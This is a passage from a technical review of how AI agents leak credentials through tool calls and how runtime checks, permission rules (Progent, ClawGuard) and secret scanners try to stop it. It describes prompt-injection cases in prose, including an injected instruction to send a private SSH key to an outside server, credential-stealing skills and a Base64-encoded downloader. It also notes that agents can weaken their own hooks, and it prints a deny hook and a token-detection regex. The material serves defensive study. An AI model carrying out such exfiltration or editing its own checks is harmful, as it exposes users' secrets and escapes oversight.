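3. Trigger: a prompt injection, a malicious tool response or an ordinary model error leads to a request that would disclose or misuse the secret.
4. Execution: the token authorises an action, such as reading or deleting data, or entering another system.
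5. Persistence: the token goes on working outside the agent, the session and the company it came from.

"Execution" here means using the secret, which can happen long after the harness executes a tool call. In call C, introduction happens when someone stores the API key in the configuration file. Propagation begins when the agent reads the file and the key enters the context. The trigger is whatever makes the model write the key into the body of the email. If the email goes out, anyone with access to the boss's mailbox can use the key (the execution stage) until the company revokes it.

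Argument inspection happens after the trigger and before the email is sent. It can keep the key out of the mailbox, but it cannot remove the copies that propagation has already made. Real leaks also skip stages. In the NordLayer case, propagation alone put production passwords on another company's servers. In Dragos's experiment, the thieves took keys from copied prompts and used them, with no tool call in between.

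Leaked credentials often remain usable for years. GitGuardian reported in March 2025 that 70 per cent of the secrets it had found leaked in 2022 were still active. Deleting a credential from the original project may not help much. Chen and colleagues disclosed leaks to developers, who removed the credentials, but found that the same credentials were still present in more than 50 independent copies of the projects.

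Kenney and colleagues argue that a system can eliminate the first two stages by keeping reusable credentials out of the model's context and the agent's working environment. They work for Corvic AI, which sells a vault for this purpose. They do not claim that this approach solves the last two stages, because an agent that never sees a token can still delete data when the token is used on its behalf. It is still necessary to limit what each token may do and how long it lasts.

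### Leaks in 17,022 skills

Chen and colleagues provide the most detailed count of where credentials leak in practice. They drew a random sample of 17,022 skills from the 170,226 on the marketplace SkillsMP and searched the code and written instructions for signs of credentials. This search ruled out 8,343 skills. They then counted a mention in the instructions only if a verb such as "send" or "store" occurred nearby, or if the text resembled prompt injection or social engineering. They counted a credential in code only if it reached a function that sends data over a network or writes to a log or file. These filters left 3,156 skills.

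The researchers ran each of these skills in an isolated container, with Claude Code as the agent and fake credentials that they could trace to the skill. Three runs used an ordinary request. In another three, outside material such as a web page contained an instruction to output the API key. Skills that showed signs of leaking in at least two ordinary runs, or in at least one run with the injected instruction, went to manual review. Three of the researchers reviewed the 1,427 skills that qualified, comparing what each one did with what its documentation described. They judged 907 to be benign, 437 vulnerable through carelessness and 83 malicious. The 520 affected skills made up 3.1 per cent of the sample and contained 1,708 separate issues.

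Comparing ordinary runs with attack runs helps separate accidental leaks from induced ones. Among the vulnerable skills, 200 leaked in at least two of the three ordinary runs. The other 237 leaked at most once in ordinary runs and at least once in attack runs. In these 237 skills, a developer carelessly left the secret accessible, and an attacker's text caused the leak. The paper also states that 466 of the 520 skills leak "during normal execution", which is hard to reconcile with these results unless normal execution includes the attack runs.

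Debug logging was the most common fault, accounting for 1,007 issues, or 73.5 per cent of the 1,371 in vulnerable skills and 59 per cent of all 1,708. Programmers often make a program print its internal values while testing it, and some forget to remove the instruction before publishing. One skill for Google's office software printed the user's access tokens. In conventional software the tokens might appear only on the developer's screen, but in an agent they enter the model's context.

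| Pattern | Issues | Skills | Where the credential goes | Does it pass through an argument? |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Information exposure (debug logging) | 1,007 | 352 | Printed output, then the model's context | No, it arrives in a tool result |
| Hardcoded credentials | 249 | 107 | The skill's published code and documents | No |
| Insecure storage | 110 | 77 | Command lines, process parameters, web addresses | Yes, though not always one the model wrote |
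| Artifact leakage | 5 | 5 | Shell history, temporary files, caches | Sometimes, since shell history keeps old commands |
| Six malicious patterns | 337 | 83 | Often an attacker's server | Seldom, since a script usually does the sending |

Only "insecure storage" consistently puts a credential in an argument, and it accounts for 6.4 per cent of all issues. A check on tool calls could detect at most that share from this group, because a script may pass the password to another program without the model writing it. Debug logging puts a credential in an argument only when the model copies a printed token into a later call, which a check on that call might stop.

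A tool call may reveal little about what the malicious skills do. One offered weather forecasts, but its script read the user's credential file and sent the contents to the attacker. The harness would receive a call to run a weather script. Another skill, which claimed to help with cryptocurrency trading, contained a command in Base64, which encodes text as a string of unfamiliar characters. The decoded command downloaded a program that searched for credentials. If the agent runs such a command through its shell tool, the argument contains the attack, but not in readable form. Of the 83 malicious skills, 37.3 per cent combined several patterns. SkillsMP has since removed all 83.

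Of the 520 cases, 76.3 per cent depended on the written instructions and the code together. For example, the instructions might tell the agent to pass the user's key to a function, which then forwards it to an undisclosed address. The instruction seems reasonable and the argument looks correct, because the code leaks the key only after receiving it.

The study covers one marketplace, and its code analysis handled only two programming languages and could follow a credential only within a single function. The analysis could lose track of a secret that a program copied into another variable, so the number of affected skills may be higher. The researchers also report that 72 per cent of the hardcoded cases had signs of AI assistance in their development history, and suggest that coding assistants spread insecure habits. Supporting that claim would require a comparison with skills that have no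 hardcoded credentials, because skill developers probably use AI assistants heavily anyway.

### How often agents put private data in arguments

*AgentLeak* gives more direct evidence than a count of faulty skills of how often agents put sensitive material in tool calls, although it covers private data such as diagnoses and account numbers, not credentials. The benchmark defines seven channels through which data can leak when several agents work together: the final output, messages between agents, tool arguments, tool results, shared memory, logs and stored files. Its 1,000 scenarios typically contain 29 private facts each, of which the task needs about three. For example, an agent booking a medical appointment needs the patient's name but not the diagnosis. The benchmark records a leak if an unneeded fact appears in any channel, even in paraphrase.

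El Yagoubi and colleagues' main evaluation, of 4,979 runs on five models, covers only final outputs, messages between agents and shared memory. They tested tool arguments separately on 100 scenarios per model, and agents sent unneeded private data to outside tools in 62 per cent (GPT-4o-mini) to 86 per cent (Llama 3.3 70B) of them. Private data appeared in logs even more often. For Claude 3.5 Sonnet, the rate was 85 per cent in logs, compared with 74 per cent in arguments, because the model's written reasoning mentioned facts that it then left out of the call.

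These rates are a weak guide to how often agents leak credentials today. All five models date from 2024, and a model may handle a password more carefully than a diagnosis. The paper also does not explain why final outputs leaked almost nothing in the smaller test, when the same models leaked in 3.3 to 47.5 per cent of final outputs in the main evaluation. El Yagoubi and colleagues list one earlier benchmark that covers tool arguments, TOP-Bench, which has 180 scenarios and tests single agents.

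The main evaluation does support the point about accidents. Messages between agents leaked in 69.3 per cent of runs with no attacker, 70.6 per cent with a weak attacker who could plant outside content, and 66.3 per cent with a strong attacker who controlled part of the system. Most of the leakage occurred because agents passed on the full background of a task when the receiving agent needed only a small part of it.

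The researchers also built a prototype that removed unneeded facts from messages and shared memory. In 120 scenarios, it cut leakage in those channels from 31.5 to 2.4 per cent, but the share of tasks completed fell from 78.6 to 73.9 per cent. In most of the lost tasks, the agents had a legitimate need to share data. Experts had also already decided which facts each task required, an advantage that a check on real requests lacks.

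## Checking a call before it runs: position, outcomes and permission rules

Runtime inspection applies complete mediation, an old principle of computer security, to tool calls. Jerome Saltzer and Michael Schroeder described the principle in 1975. It requires a system to check that every access to every object is authorized. For an agent, this means that every call must pass the check before it reaches a tool. Work on operating systems from the same period added that the program being checked must be unable to alter the check.

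Agents make the second requirement harder to meet because many of them can edit files. Claude Code, for example, lets users attach programs called hooks that run before each tool call. Users define hooks in settings files, and the hooks' scripts are often in the project folder where the agent works. According to Anthropic's hook reference, Claude Code normally picks up edits to hooks automatically. An agent with permission to write to those files could therefore weaken its own check. A company can reduce this risk by installing hooks through centrally managed settings, because users' own settings cannot switch those hooks off.

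### Logging, filtering and sandboxing

Logging is one of three other defences that overlap with runtime inspection. It records a call after it has run. Claude Code also offers a hook that runs at that point and receives both the arguments and the result, but by then call B's email has been sent. A company can still use the log to identify which key to revoke.

Filtering happens earlier, on the text the agent reads. In *Progent*, Shi, He and colleagues (2025) tested three detectors of this kind on AgentDojo and found that the detectors missed many attacks and raised many false alarms.

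Sandboxing limits what a program can do while it runs, for example by denying it network access. It can therefore restrict actions that never appear in a tool call's arguments. *Towards Practically-Secure Tools for AI Agents* (Adam, Lu and colleagues, 2026) gives the example of a file-writing tool that also reports each file's size to a statistics service. Neither the tool's description nor the call mentions the report, so a check on arguments would miss it, but a sandbox without network access would stop it.

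Most sandboxes apply one fixed policy to every task, which is their weakness. If the policy permits connections to the mail server, calls A, B and C can all go out. Adam and colleagues also observed Claude 4.5 Haiku copy a configuration file containing an API key into a new project and then publish the project on GitHub, as the user had asked. Each step was a normal use of its tool. The researchers argue that a fixed policy could prevent this only with a blanket restriction, such as blocking all network access, which users would soon disable.

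Their own design combines the two approaches. A program analyses the tool's code in advance and lists its possible effects, and small sandboxes inside the tool enforce a policy that arrives with each call. So far they have tried a prototype on one real MCP server, and the design depends on tool developers adding the sandboxes to their code.

### Where to put the check

A check can sit in any of four places between the model and the outside world.

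| Position | What the check receives | What escapes it |
|---|---|---|
| Library code inside the agent program | Tool name and arguments, and the user's request if the developer passes it on | Network requests and file changes that a tool's own code makes |
| Hook that the harness runs before each call | Tool name and arguments | The same, plus text that enters the context without a tool call, and any tool the hook's filter misses |
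| MCP gateway between the agent and its MCP servers | Name and arguments of each call to those servers | Built-in tools, such as a shell or file editor |
| Network exit, where traffic leaves the machine | Destination of each connection, and its contents if the gateway can decrypt them | Local actions, such as deleting a file, and misuse of permitted hosts |

Running the check in a library suits developers who write their own agents. Anthropic's software development kit, for instance, lets a developer register a function that receives each tool's name and arguments, then allows, blocks or modifies the call. An example in its documentation blocks any write to a `.env` file.

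Shi and colleagues offer their rule system, Progent, as a proxy for people who use someone else's agent and cannot change its code. The user routes the agent's connections to the model and to its MCP servers through Progent. This can work even with closed-source products, but it does not protect built-in tools that bypass MCP. In a coding agent, these often include the shell, which can do more damage than almost any other tool.

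Hooks in Claude Code cover both built-in and MCP tools, including calls by subagents. Each hook has a filter that specifies which tools it applies to, but Anthropic documents several ways for a filter to miss tools it is meant to cover. A filter for "Bash", for example, does not apply to commands that Claude Code runs through its separate PowerShell tool, which it prefers on Windows wherever that tool is enabled. To cover every tool on a mail server named "mail", a filter must read `mcp__mail__.*`, because `mcp__mail` matches no tool. Hooks can also filter by the content of shell commands, but Anthropic describes that filter as "best-effort" and recommends Claude Code's separate permission settings for firm prohibitions.

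Some actions also bypass the hook because the model makes no tool call. When a user types "@" and a file name, Claude Code inserts the file's contents directly into the prompt. A hook on the file-reading tool therefore does not run, even if the file contains passwords. Users can block this with a permission rule that denies access to the file. Similarly, a hook on the tool that loads skills runs when the model chooses a skill, but not when the user types the skill's name.

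A check at the network exit can catch traffic that the other three miss, such as a skill's script sending a stolen key to an unknown server. But it has little information about the purpose of a connection. Calls A and C, for example, go to the same mail server, and the user's request never reaches the network exit.

### Allow, block, rewrite or ask

The simplest outcomes are to allow a call or to block it. A hook in Claude Code could block call B by returning this answer:

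```json
{
  "hookSpecificOutput": {
    "hookEventName": "PreToolUse",
    "permissionDecision": "deny",
    "permissionDecisionReason": "Recipient not allowed for this task"
  }
}
```

Claude Code then passes the reason to the model, which can carry on with the task. Progent does the same by default. Its message explains the refusal, repeats the user's request and suggests trying other tools or arguments. This lets the agent still send the summary to the boss after an attack. But an agent still under the attacker's influence may look for another way to reach the same goal, so the rules have to cover that too.

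When several hooks check one call, Claude Code applies the strictest decision. Crosley's *Claude Code Hooks Explained* adds that a hook can block a call even when the user has turned off all permission prompts, but cannot allow a call that the settings prohibit.

A check can also rewrite a call. For call C, it could delete the API key from the body and send the rest of the summary. The risk is that one check approves a call and another then changes it. In Claude Code's auto mode, a separate model reviews the arguments the agent wrote, in place of the user. If a hook then changes them, Claude Code may refuse the new version until the agent submits it for review. *ClawGuard* (Zhao, Li and colleagues, 2026) avoids the problem by removing secrets first and applying its other rules to the result. But removing every secret would break call D, because the code host would receive a placeholder where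 it needs the token.

The remaining outcome is to hold the call until a person answers. Claude Code can show the user a prompt or, when another program is running it, pause so that the program can collect an answer. If the model has made several calls at once, Claude Code ignores the instruction to pause and applies its normal permission rules.

### When the check fails

Any check can crash, time out or return an unreadable answer. A system fails open if it then runs the call anyway, and fails closed if it blocks the call.

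Claude Code's hooks mostly fail open. A script blocks a call by exiting with code 2, while code 1, the usual Unix code for failure, normally lets the call continue. A mistyped file path normally lets it continue too, because the script never starts. If a hook exceeds its time limit, the call goes through the normal permission process, which may stop it. Since version 2.1.295, users have been able to make a hook fail closed by adding the setting `"onFailure": "block"`. Functions that developers register through Anthropic's software kit block the call when they time out, even without this setting.

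OpenGuard's *llm_tool_inspection* describes a check that sends tool descriptions, arguments and results to a second language model. If the inspection fails, the default setting allows the call. The check sends at most 8,000 characters by default, so the second model may not receive all of a long conversation.

Failing open is convenient for developers because one broken script does not halt all their work. But it is dangerous when an attacker can cause the failure, for example by getting the agent to write an argument so long that the check times out. A check that guards secrets or payments should therefore fail closed, while one that only formats code can safely fail open.

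Designers must also choose how to handle calls that no rule mentions. Saltzer and Schroeder recommended refusing access unless a rule grants it, because the designer of a list of prohibitions must foresee every danger. Progent follows this advice and blocks such calls. Zhao and colleagues' ClawGuard treats them as ambiguous and asks the user, then blocks the call if the user doesn't answer in time.

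### How well people review calls

Asking a person for approval seems the safest option only if that person reads the request. Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode* describes "approval fatigue", in which people who approve many actions stop paying close attention to them. Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (August 2026) reports that users approve 97 per cent of permission prompts. Most of those requests are probably harmless, so the figure alone does not prove that users are careless.

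According to the blog Hyrax, human testers in an Anthropic experiment stopped 143 of 1,053 dangerous commands, or 13.6 per cent. They stopped about 17 per cent early in a session and about 5 per cent after 50 or more permission prompts. An automated classifier stopped 937 of the same commands, or 89 per cent. Anthropic used this comparison to justify replacing most permission prompts with its own classifier, so it had an interest in the result.

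Even the early rate was low, so fatigue cannot be the whole explanation. Adam and colleagues point out that a permission prompt assumes the user understands what a shell command will do. Hyrax reports that users reject 39 per cent of the plans Claude Code shows them. This suggests that people review one readable proposal more carefully than dozens of commands, although they may reject a plan for reasons unrelated to safety.

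Permission rules can reduce the number of prompts by settling the clear cases in advance.

### A small rule set for the example calls

A permission rule defines which tools an agent may call and with what arguments. The simplest kind is a stricter argument schema, such as one that limits `send_email` to a fixed list of recipients. Progent's rules use the same format, JSON Schema, which allows fixed values, lists and text patterns.

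The following rules cover the two tasks from the first section. Calls A and D are harmless, B sends a report to the attacker, and C includes an API key in the email to the boss.

```text
Task 1: summarise a page and email the summary to the boss
  allow  fetch_page    when  url == "https://news.example/article"
  allow  send_email    when  recipient == "boss@company.com"
```

Task 2: list the open issues in a software project
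  allow  http_request  when  url == "https://api.codehost.example/issues"

Block every other call.
```

| Call | Rules | Result | Correct? |
|---|---|---|---|
| A | Task 1 | Allowed, because the recipient matches | Yes |
| B | Task 1 | Blocked, because the recipient does not match | Yes |
| C | Task 1 | Allowed, because the recipient matches | No |
| D | Task 2 | Allowed, because the address matches | Yes |

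C passes because the only condition on `send_email` concerns the recipient, and C has the right recipient. Nobody can add an equally exact condition for the body, because the agent doesn't write the body until it has read the page. A rule could limit the body's length or forbid text that looks like an API key, but checking for keys means searching for secrets, which requires a list of what secrets look like.

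D passes because the rule allows its web address. The rule ignores the headers, so it would also allow a request that sent the company's Amazon key to the code host.

Small errors in the rules can let B through as well. Many email tools have fields for additional recipients, so a rule that checks only the main recipient allows an attacker to receive a copy. A pattern can also be too loose, as when a rule that accepts any address containing "company.com" accepts boss@company.com.attacker.example. Anthropic warns of the same effect in its hook filters, where the pattern `Edit.*`, apparently meant for one tool, also matches NotebookEdit.

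Lists of permitted hosts are also limited because one host can serve many people. A rule that allows GitHub for a coding task does not distinguish the company's private repository from a public one unless it also checks the rest of the address or the account.

Most companies could write a general list of permitted addresses once, such as all those at company.com. But that list would not have stopped Now Assist's agents from leaking a confidential ticket, because they sent nothing outside the company. Rules for a single task are much tighter, but each request needs its own. Progent and ClawGuard both use a language model to write them.

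### Progent: checking changes to the rules

A Progent rule specifies a tool, whether to allow or forbid it, and conditions on its arguments. The conditions can compare numbers, match text patterns or test whether a value is in a list. Progent applies the forbid rules first, then the allow rules, and blocks any call that matches neither. This step uses no language model, so the same call under the same rules always gets the same result.

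A model writes the rules. Before the agent starts, it produces an initial set from the user's request and the list of tools. Shi and colleagues assume that this stage is free of the attacker's text because the request comes from the user. But the request often lacks enough detail to show which tools the agent will need. In their example, a user asks an agent to carry out the tasks in an email from Alice. The initial rules can allow only a search for that email. The tasks turn out to be summarizing recent messages and posting the summary on the user's Slack, so the agent needs more tools.

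Progent therefore lets the model propose new rules as the task proceeds. It first asks the model whether a call might require an update, without showing it the result of that call. If the answer is yes, the model receives the result and writes new rules. At this point an attacker's text can influence it, so Progent compares the new rules with the old:

```text
A(P)  =  the set of all calls that rules P allow

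Changing P to P' is a narrowing  if  A(P') ⊆ A(P)
                 an expansion    otherwise
```

An SMT solver, a program that determines whether any values can satisfy a set of logical conditions, compares the new rules with the old ones. It searches for a call that the new rules allow and the old rules do not. If there is none, the change is a narrowing and takes effect at once. Otherwise it is an expansion and needs approval. In the example, adding the Slack tool is an expansion. After the agent looks up the user's Slack name, limiting messages to that name is a narrowing. A later email contains an instruction to forward the inbox to an attacker. Following it would require adding the email tool, another expansion, which the approver can refuse.

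The guarantee is only that the set of permitted calls never grows without approval, and the permitted calls may still be unsafe. Between the first and second changes in the example, the rules allowed a Slack message to anyone. If the agent had read the attacker's email then, it could have sent the attacker a Slack message without breaking a rule. An update that limited messages to the attacker's name would have counted as a narrowing, so it would have taken effect automatically.

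Shi and colleagues tested Progent with GPT-4o both running the agent and writing the rules. On AgentDojo, Progent reduced the attack success rate from 39.9 to 1.0 per cent while largely preserving the agent's usefulness. They left out two AgentDojo attacks that tried to make the agent prefer a particular hotel, because Progent is not designed to stop an attacker from influencing a choice among permitted options. On ASB, a second benchmark with ten kinds of agent, the rate fell from 70.3 to 3.9 per cent. Most of the remaining failures on ASB involved harmful tools with names and descriptions very similar to those of legitimate ones. Rules that the researchers wrote by hand stopped all of those attacks.

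Results on AgentDojo also support checking arguments as well as tool names. An earlier defence, which asks a model which tools a task needs and removes the rest, stopped fewer attacks than Progent and disrupted more legitimate work, because a harmless call and an attack can use the same tool, as A and B do.

In these main tests, Progent approved every expansion automatically, to represent a careless user. The 1.0 per cent therefore does not measure the guarantee, which requires someone to refuse bad expansions. It depends partly on GPT-4o not proposing harmful rules after reading the attacker's text. *Extending the Formalism and Theoretical Foundations of Cryptography to AI* (2026) warns that hostile tool results may cause updates to relax the rules, and that Progent's protection depends on the rules being correct and complete.

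With the initial rules and no updates, the attack success rate was 2.5 per cent, so most of the protection came from rules written before the agent read anything. When a person reviewed the initial rules and every expansion, the rate fell to zero. That result assumes a reviewer with strong security awareness who would always reject a malicious address, and the testers in Anthropic's experiment fell far short of that standard. Progent rarely needs a person to review an update, though, as only 6 per cent of updates were expansions.

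### ClawGuard: fixing the rules before the first call

ClawGuard derives its task rules only from the user's request and does not change them during the task. Before the first tool call, the model running the agent generates lists of permitted and forbidden websites, files and commands. The user can edit these lists before confirming them. Separate baseline rules apply to every task and take priority over the task rules. They block access to stored credentials, changes to the agent's own configuration, irreversible system commands and transfers to unapproved destinations.

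In one worked example, a user asks an agent to summarize three blog posts and save the summary to a file. ClawGuard's rules permit access to the blog's address and the reports folder and forbid shell commands. The third post contains an instruction to send an outside server the user's private SSH key, which gives access to other computers. The agent attempts this with a shell command, but the task rule against shell commands and the baseline rule against opening the key's folder each block it independently. The agent then saves the summary.

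If a call involves several items, such as a command and a file, ClawGuard applies the strictest result. It asks the user about commands that appear disguised, for example in Base64 encoding, because its rules cannot match the hidden text. It also has a language model examine each new skill once, before its first use.

Zhao and colleagues tested ClawGuard in OpenClaw, an agent program that runs on the user's own machine, with five models including GPT-5.4 and Claude Sonnet 4.6. On AgentDojo, at least 95.88 per cent of attacks failed without an added defence, and all of them failed with ClawGuard. In the Progent study, 39.9 per cent of attacks succeeded against GPT-4o. The difference suggests that newer models already resist many of the benchmark's attacks, although the two studies used different agent programs and selections of attacks.

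Attacks hidden in skills or tool descriptions were harder to resist. The table gives the share of attacks that failed, averaged across the five models.

| Benchmark | Source of the attack | No added defence | With ClawGuard |
|---|---|---|---|
| SkillInject | Skill files | 56.67% | 86.67% |
| MCPTox | MCP tools | 62.10% | 89.50% |
| MCPSecurityBench | MCP tools | 75.86% | 94.21% |

Most of the attacks that still succeeded on SkillInject required no forbidden tool or destination. One instructed the agent to give high scores to the websites of environmentally friendly companies without reviewing them. Another had it delete paragraphs that mentioned climate or diversity from a document it was editing. A permission rule can check whether the agent may edit the document, but not whether the user wanted that edit. Call C similarly passes the recipient rule because the harm is in the content.

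To measure the cost, the researchers ran ordinary web, operating-system and programming tasks without attacks. The following figures show how much of the agent's original success rate remained, on average, when ClawGuard refused every call that needed approval and when it allowed up to three approvals per task:

| Tasks | No approvals | Up to three approvals |
|---|---|---|
| Web browsing | 78.5% | 91.7% |
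| Operating system | 88.8% | 94.9% |
| Programming | 94.9% | 98.8% |
| Average | 87.4% | 95.1% |

Browsing suffered most because it involves many pages that nobody can list in advance. ClawGuard also used about 5 per cent more tokens.

In the attack tests, ClawGuard automatically refused every call that needed approval, so the defence rates correspond only to the column without approvals, where the agent's success rate fell by about an eighth. The study does not show how many attacks would succeed if a tired user approved the ambiguous calls, so the security of the setting with approvals is unknown.

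The model that writes the rules affects both how well ClawGuard protects an agent and how much it interferes with ordinary tasks. Without approvals, ClawGuard reduced GPT-5.4's success on ordinary tasks by 8.1 per cent and DeepSeek-V3.2's by 21.6 per cent. In a further test on suspicious skills from a public collection, the strongest models running with ClawGuard stopped 94 per cent of attempts to steal data, and the weakest stopped 67 per cent. Zhao and colleagues attribute the difference to imprecise rules and skill inspections, which led ClawGuard to treat some malicious actions as part of the user's task.

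## Scanning arguments for secrets and attack patterns

The recipient rule allowed call C because it did not check the body of the email. A content scanner searches the text of every argument for credentials and signs of known attacks, such as a command that deletes a database table.

In August 2025, GitHub's remote MCP server, which lets agents work with code repositories, began scanning for secrets in the arguments of every call that involves a public repository (GitHub, 2025). If the server finds a secret, it blocks the call by default and returns an explanation, with a link for users who want to send the secret anyway. According to GitHub's documentation, the protection also applies to private repositories covered by GitHub Advanced Security. The scan runs on GitHub's side, so a key in a blocked call has already reached GitHub, but the block stops the agent from posting the key in a public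 issue, where anyone could copy it.

### Prefixes, formats and checksums

A secret is easiest to recognise when its issuer has marked it. Many of GitHub's older tokens were strings of 40 hexadecimal digits (0 to 9 and a to f), the same format as the hashes that identify versions of files, so a scanner could not tell the two apart. *Behind GitHub's new authentication token formats* (2021) describes the prefixes that GitHub added. Personal access tokens, like the one in call D, begin with "ghp_", and OAuth tokens with "gho_". Standard Base64 does not use the underscore, so random data in that encoding cannot contain the prefix. GitHub expected the prefix alone to bring the false-positive rate down to 0.5 per cent.

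The last six characters of these tokens are a checksum, so a scanner can recompute it with a standard calculation and discard any string that does not match, without contacting GitHub. The checksum has 32 bits, so a random string with the right prefix passes about once in 4.3 billion cases. A match does not show whether the token still works.

Scanners usually describe each format with a regular expression, a pattern that specifies which characters may appear and in what order. These patterns need maintenance. In April 2026 GitHub announced that one kind of token, which begins with "ghs_", would grow from 40 characters to about 520. The new version has the application's number after the prefix, then another underscore and a long encoded section. A scanner that expects 36 letters or digits straight after the prefix will miss it, because the second underscore interrupts them. In May GitHub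 recommended a pattern that matches both versions:

```text
ghs_[A-Za-z0-9\.\-_]{36,}
```

It accepts "ghs_" followed by at least 36 letters, digits, dots, hyphens or underscores.

Some credentials have no distinctive format. *SecretSifter* (2026), a scanner for web traffic, has 134 rules for recognisable formats and another 52 that apply only if a keyword associated with the vendor appears near the value. In a tool call, the argument's name sometimes provides such a keyword, since a value in an argument called "password" is probably a password. In the body of an email, a scanner can only look for keywords in the text the model wrote.

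A prefix does not always identify the issuer. Semgrep's *Secrets Story* points out that DeepSeek's keys and OpenAI's older keys both start with "sk-" and otherwise look alike. A scanner can recognise such a string as a key without identifying which company should receive it.

### Randomness measured by Shannon entropy

To find secrets in unknown formats, many scanners measure how random a string looks. The usual measure is Shannon entropy:

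```text
H = − Σ pᵢ log₂ pᵢ
```

Here pᵢ is the fraction of the string made up of character i, and the sum covers each distinct character. The result is in bits per character. A string made of one repeated character has zero entropy, and a string with no repeated characters has the highest entropy possible for its length.

The word "calendar" has eight letters. The letter "a" appears twice and the other six each appear once. The invented key "k7Qz2mXw9RtB4vLp" has 16 characters, all different.

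```text
calendar           H = (2/8 × 2) + 6 × (1/8 × 3)  =  2.75
k7Qz2mXw9RtB4vLp   H = 16 × (1/16 × 4)            =  4.00
```

SecretSifter uses a default cutoff of 3.5. Gitleaks, a widely used open-source scanner, uses the same default for secrets without a known format. The key is above this cutoff and the word is below it.

The entropy formula leads to both missed secrets and false alarms. A string of n characters cannot have an entropy above log₂ n, which is 3.46 for 11 characters, so a cutoff of 3.5 misses every password of 11 characters or fewer, however random. Longer ordinary text can exceed the cutoff. "Here is a summary of the page", from the harmless call A, has an entropy of 3.68, so a scanner has to measure unbroken strings rather than whole sentences. The formula also ignores the order of the characters, so "abcdefghijklmnop" gets the same 4.00 as the key.

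Raising the cutoff reduces false alarms but lets more secrets through. The monitor in *Cross-Layer Semantic Flow Reconstruction for Attack Detection in Agentic Systems* (2026) prompts a language model to treat strings with an entropy above 4.0 as secrets. The invented key falls just short of that cutoff. A hexadecimal key of any length is also missed, because with only 16 possible digits its entropy cannot exceed 4.0.

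Entropy can also help remove false alarms. *Agent Audit* (2026), which scans the code of agent applications, first looks for known formats and then uses entropy to discard placeholders, such as a row of x's where a key should go.

*Rare Not Random*, by the creator of Gitleaks, compares entropy with a measure called token efficiency on CredData, a collection of labelled strings from real code repositories. Token efficiency is the length of a string divided by the number of tokens a language model's tokenizer splits it into. Common words stay in long pieces, while random strings break into short ones. "lookingatcomputer" has 17 characters and splits into three tokens, an efficiency of 5.7. An invented GitHub token of 24 characters splits into 22 tokens, an efficiency of 1.1. The filter flags strings below 2.5 as secrets. In the table, precision is the share of flagged strings that were real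 secrets, and recall is the share of real secrets that the filter flagged.

| Filter | Precision | Recall |
|---|---|---|
| Entropy | 21.1% | 70.4% |
| Entropy, with a filter for common words | 76.6% | 67.1% |
| Token efficiency | 57.3% | 98.6% |
| Token efficiency, with a filter for common words | 80.4% | 95.8% |

With entropy alone, nearly four in five alarms were false. These figures cover only strings already picked out as possible secrets, so they do not show how either filter would perform on a whole email. The author is also building token efficiency into Betterleaks, his successor to Gitleaks. He concedes that token efficiency does badly on weak passwords such as "password123", which the tokenizer handles much like ordinary language.

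### Known secrets and a test of nine defences

If an organisation keeps a list of its secrets, a scanner can search each argument for those exact values, including passwords that no pattern would recognise. The list would be valuable to a thief, so the scanner can instead store a fingerprint of each secret, which is a value calculated from the secret that does not reveal it, at least if the secret is long and random. The scanner then calculates fingerprints for every stretch of text that is the same length as a secret and compares them with the stored ones. Short passwords can cause false alarms, because a password such as "summer" also appears in harmless emails.

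In *Evaluation of Prompt Injection Defenses in Large Language Models*, Deep, Emmons and colleagues (2026) tested a simple form of this search on a chatbot's replies rather than on tool calls. They put three secrets in the chatbot's standing instructions and had a second language model try to extract them. The attacker wrote ten prompts per round and used the replies to improve the next ten. One defence was a short program that blocked any reply containing text from the standing instructions.

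There were nine configurations. With no defence, the chatbot revealed everything within the first 25 rounds. The next table shows when seven of the other configurations first had a severe leak, meaning a score of at least 0.9 out of 1.

| Defence | First severe leak |
|---|---|
| Screening the user's messages | Round 39 |
| Instructions never to reveal credentials | Round 49 |
| Marking the user's text as data | Round 84 |
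| Ranking instructions by priority | Round 247 |
| Security rules at both ends of the prompt | Round 277 |
| Program that checks replies | None in 500 rounds |
| All of the above together | None in 500 rounds |

The researchers then ran each of the last two configurations three times, with 5,000 attacks per run, and recorded no leaks. They report a total of 15,000 attacks, but six runs of 5,000 make 30,000, so 15,000 is the number for each configuration.

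This result is less surprising than it looks, because the program that scored the attacks also searched for literal text. If an attacker had got the chatbot to write a secret in Base64, the filter would have let it through and the scoring program would have recorded no leak. Deep and colleagues acknowledge that encoding and rewording can evade both. They did not report how often the filter blocked harmless replies. Most of them work for Swept AI, which sells security testing for AI systems.

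The ninth configuration combined every defence except the filter. Of 5,000 attacks, 23 produced a leak, and the highest score was 0.1. A single secret would have scored 0.3, so these leaks contained only fragments of the instructions or the chatbot's name. Together, these defences protected the secrets in this run, although each failed alone.

One advantage carries over to tool arguments. Prompt injection cannot change the result of a text search, however the attacker persuaded the model to write the secret. But the test was easier than inspecting an agent's calls. The filter had a complete list of the secrets, whereas an agent may open a file containing a key that nobody has listed. The chatbot also never had a good reason to reveal a secret, so every match was a leak, but call D has to include the token.

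### What existing scanners miss

Scanners can miss even the formats they are designed to recognise. In *Boundary-Mutation Testing for Pattern-Based Secret Detection*, Mishra (2026) tested three scanners on ten types of artificial credentials, placed in different surroundings such as a configuration file, a web address or a function call. In the basic comparison, each scanner found either every example of a type or none. Mishra's own scanner, GitHub Autopilot, found all ten types, Gitleaks found eight or nine, depending on how realistic the artificial tokens were, and TruffleHog found six. Mishra does not rank them because ten types are too few for a reliable comparison.

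Detection often depended more on the text around a credential than on the credential itself. Gitleaks found an Amazon key in quotation marks but missed the same key in `f(AKIA...)`. Its rules for six types of credential accept only certain characters after the secret, and these don't include a closing bracket, a comma or an ampersand. A scanner with this fault could therefore miss a key that an agent puts in a URL argument such as `?key=SECRET&next=1`. Call C would be easier to catch if the key came at the very end of the email's body, because the rules do accept the end of the text.

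TruffleHog, by contrast, was unaffected by surrounding punctuation, but it reported an Amazon key only when it also found the second secret that normally accompanies it. Mishra's scanner missed keys for the email service SendGrid if they ended in a hyphen, as about one in 64 should.

*Secrets That Survive Everything* (Gorijala, 2026) tested nine scanners on 194 real credentials collected from one organisation's web applications. The best scanner designed for source code found 36.6 per cent of them, and the best one designed for live applications found 77.8 per cent. All nine missed the same 27 credentials, or 13.9 per cent. Some credentials were encrypted and stored beside their decryption key, so they were readable only after decryption. The organisation relied heavily on Microsoft's Azure services, and the rates could be quite different elsewhere.

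*NovaFabric* (2026), a tool that records what agents do, uses the Gitleaks rules to remove secrets from its recordings. Agents commonly handle private keys, bearer tokens, passwords, database connection strings and several kinds of cloud key, but the tool's documentation lists all of these as things its scanner does not cover.

### How AEGIS checks a call

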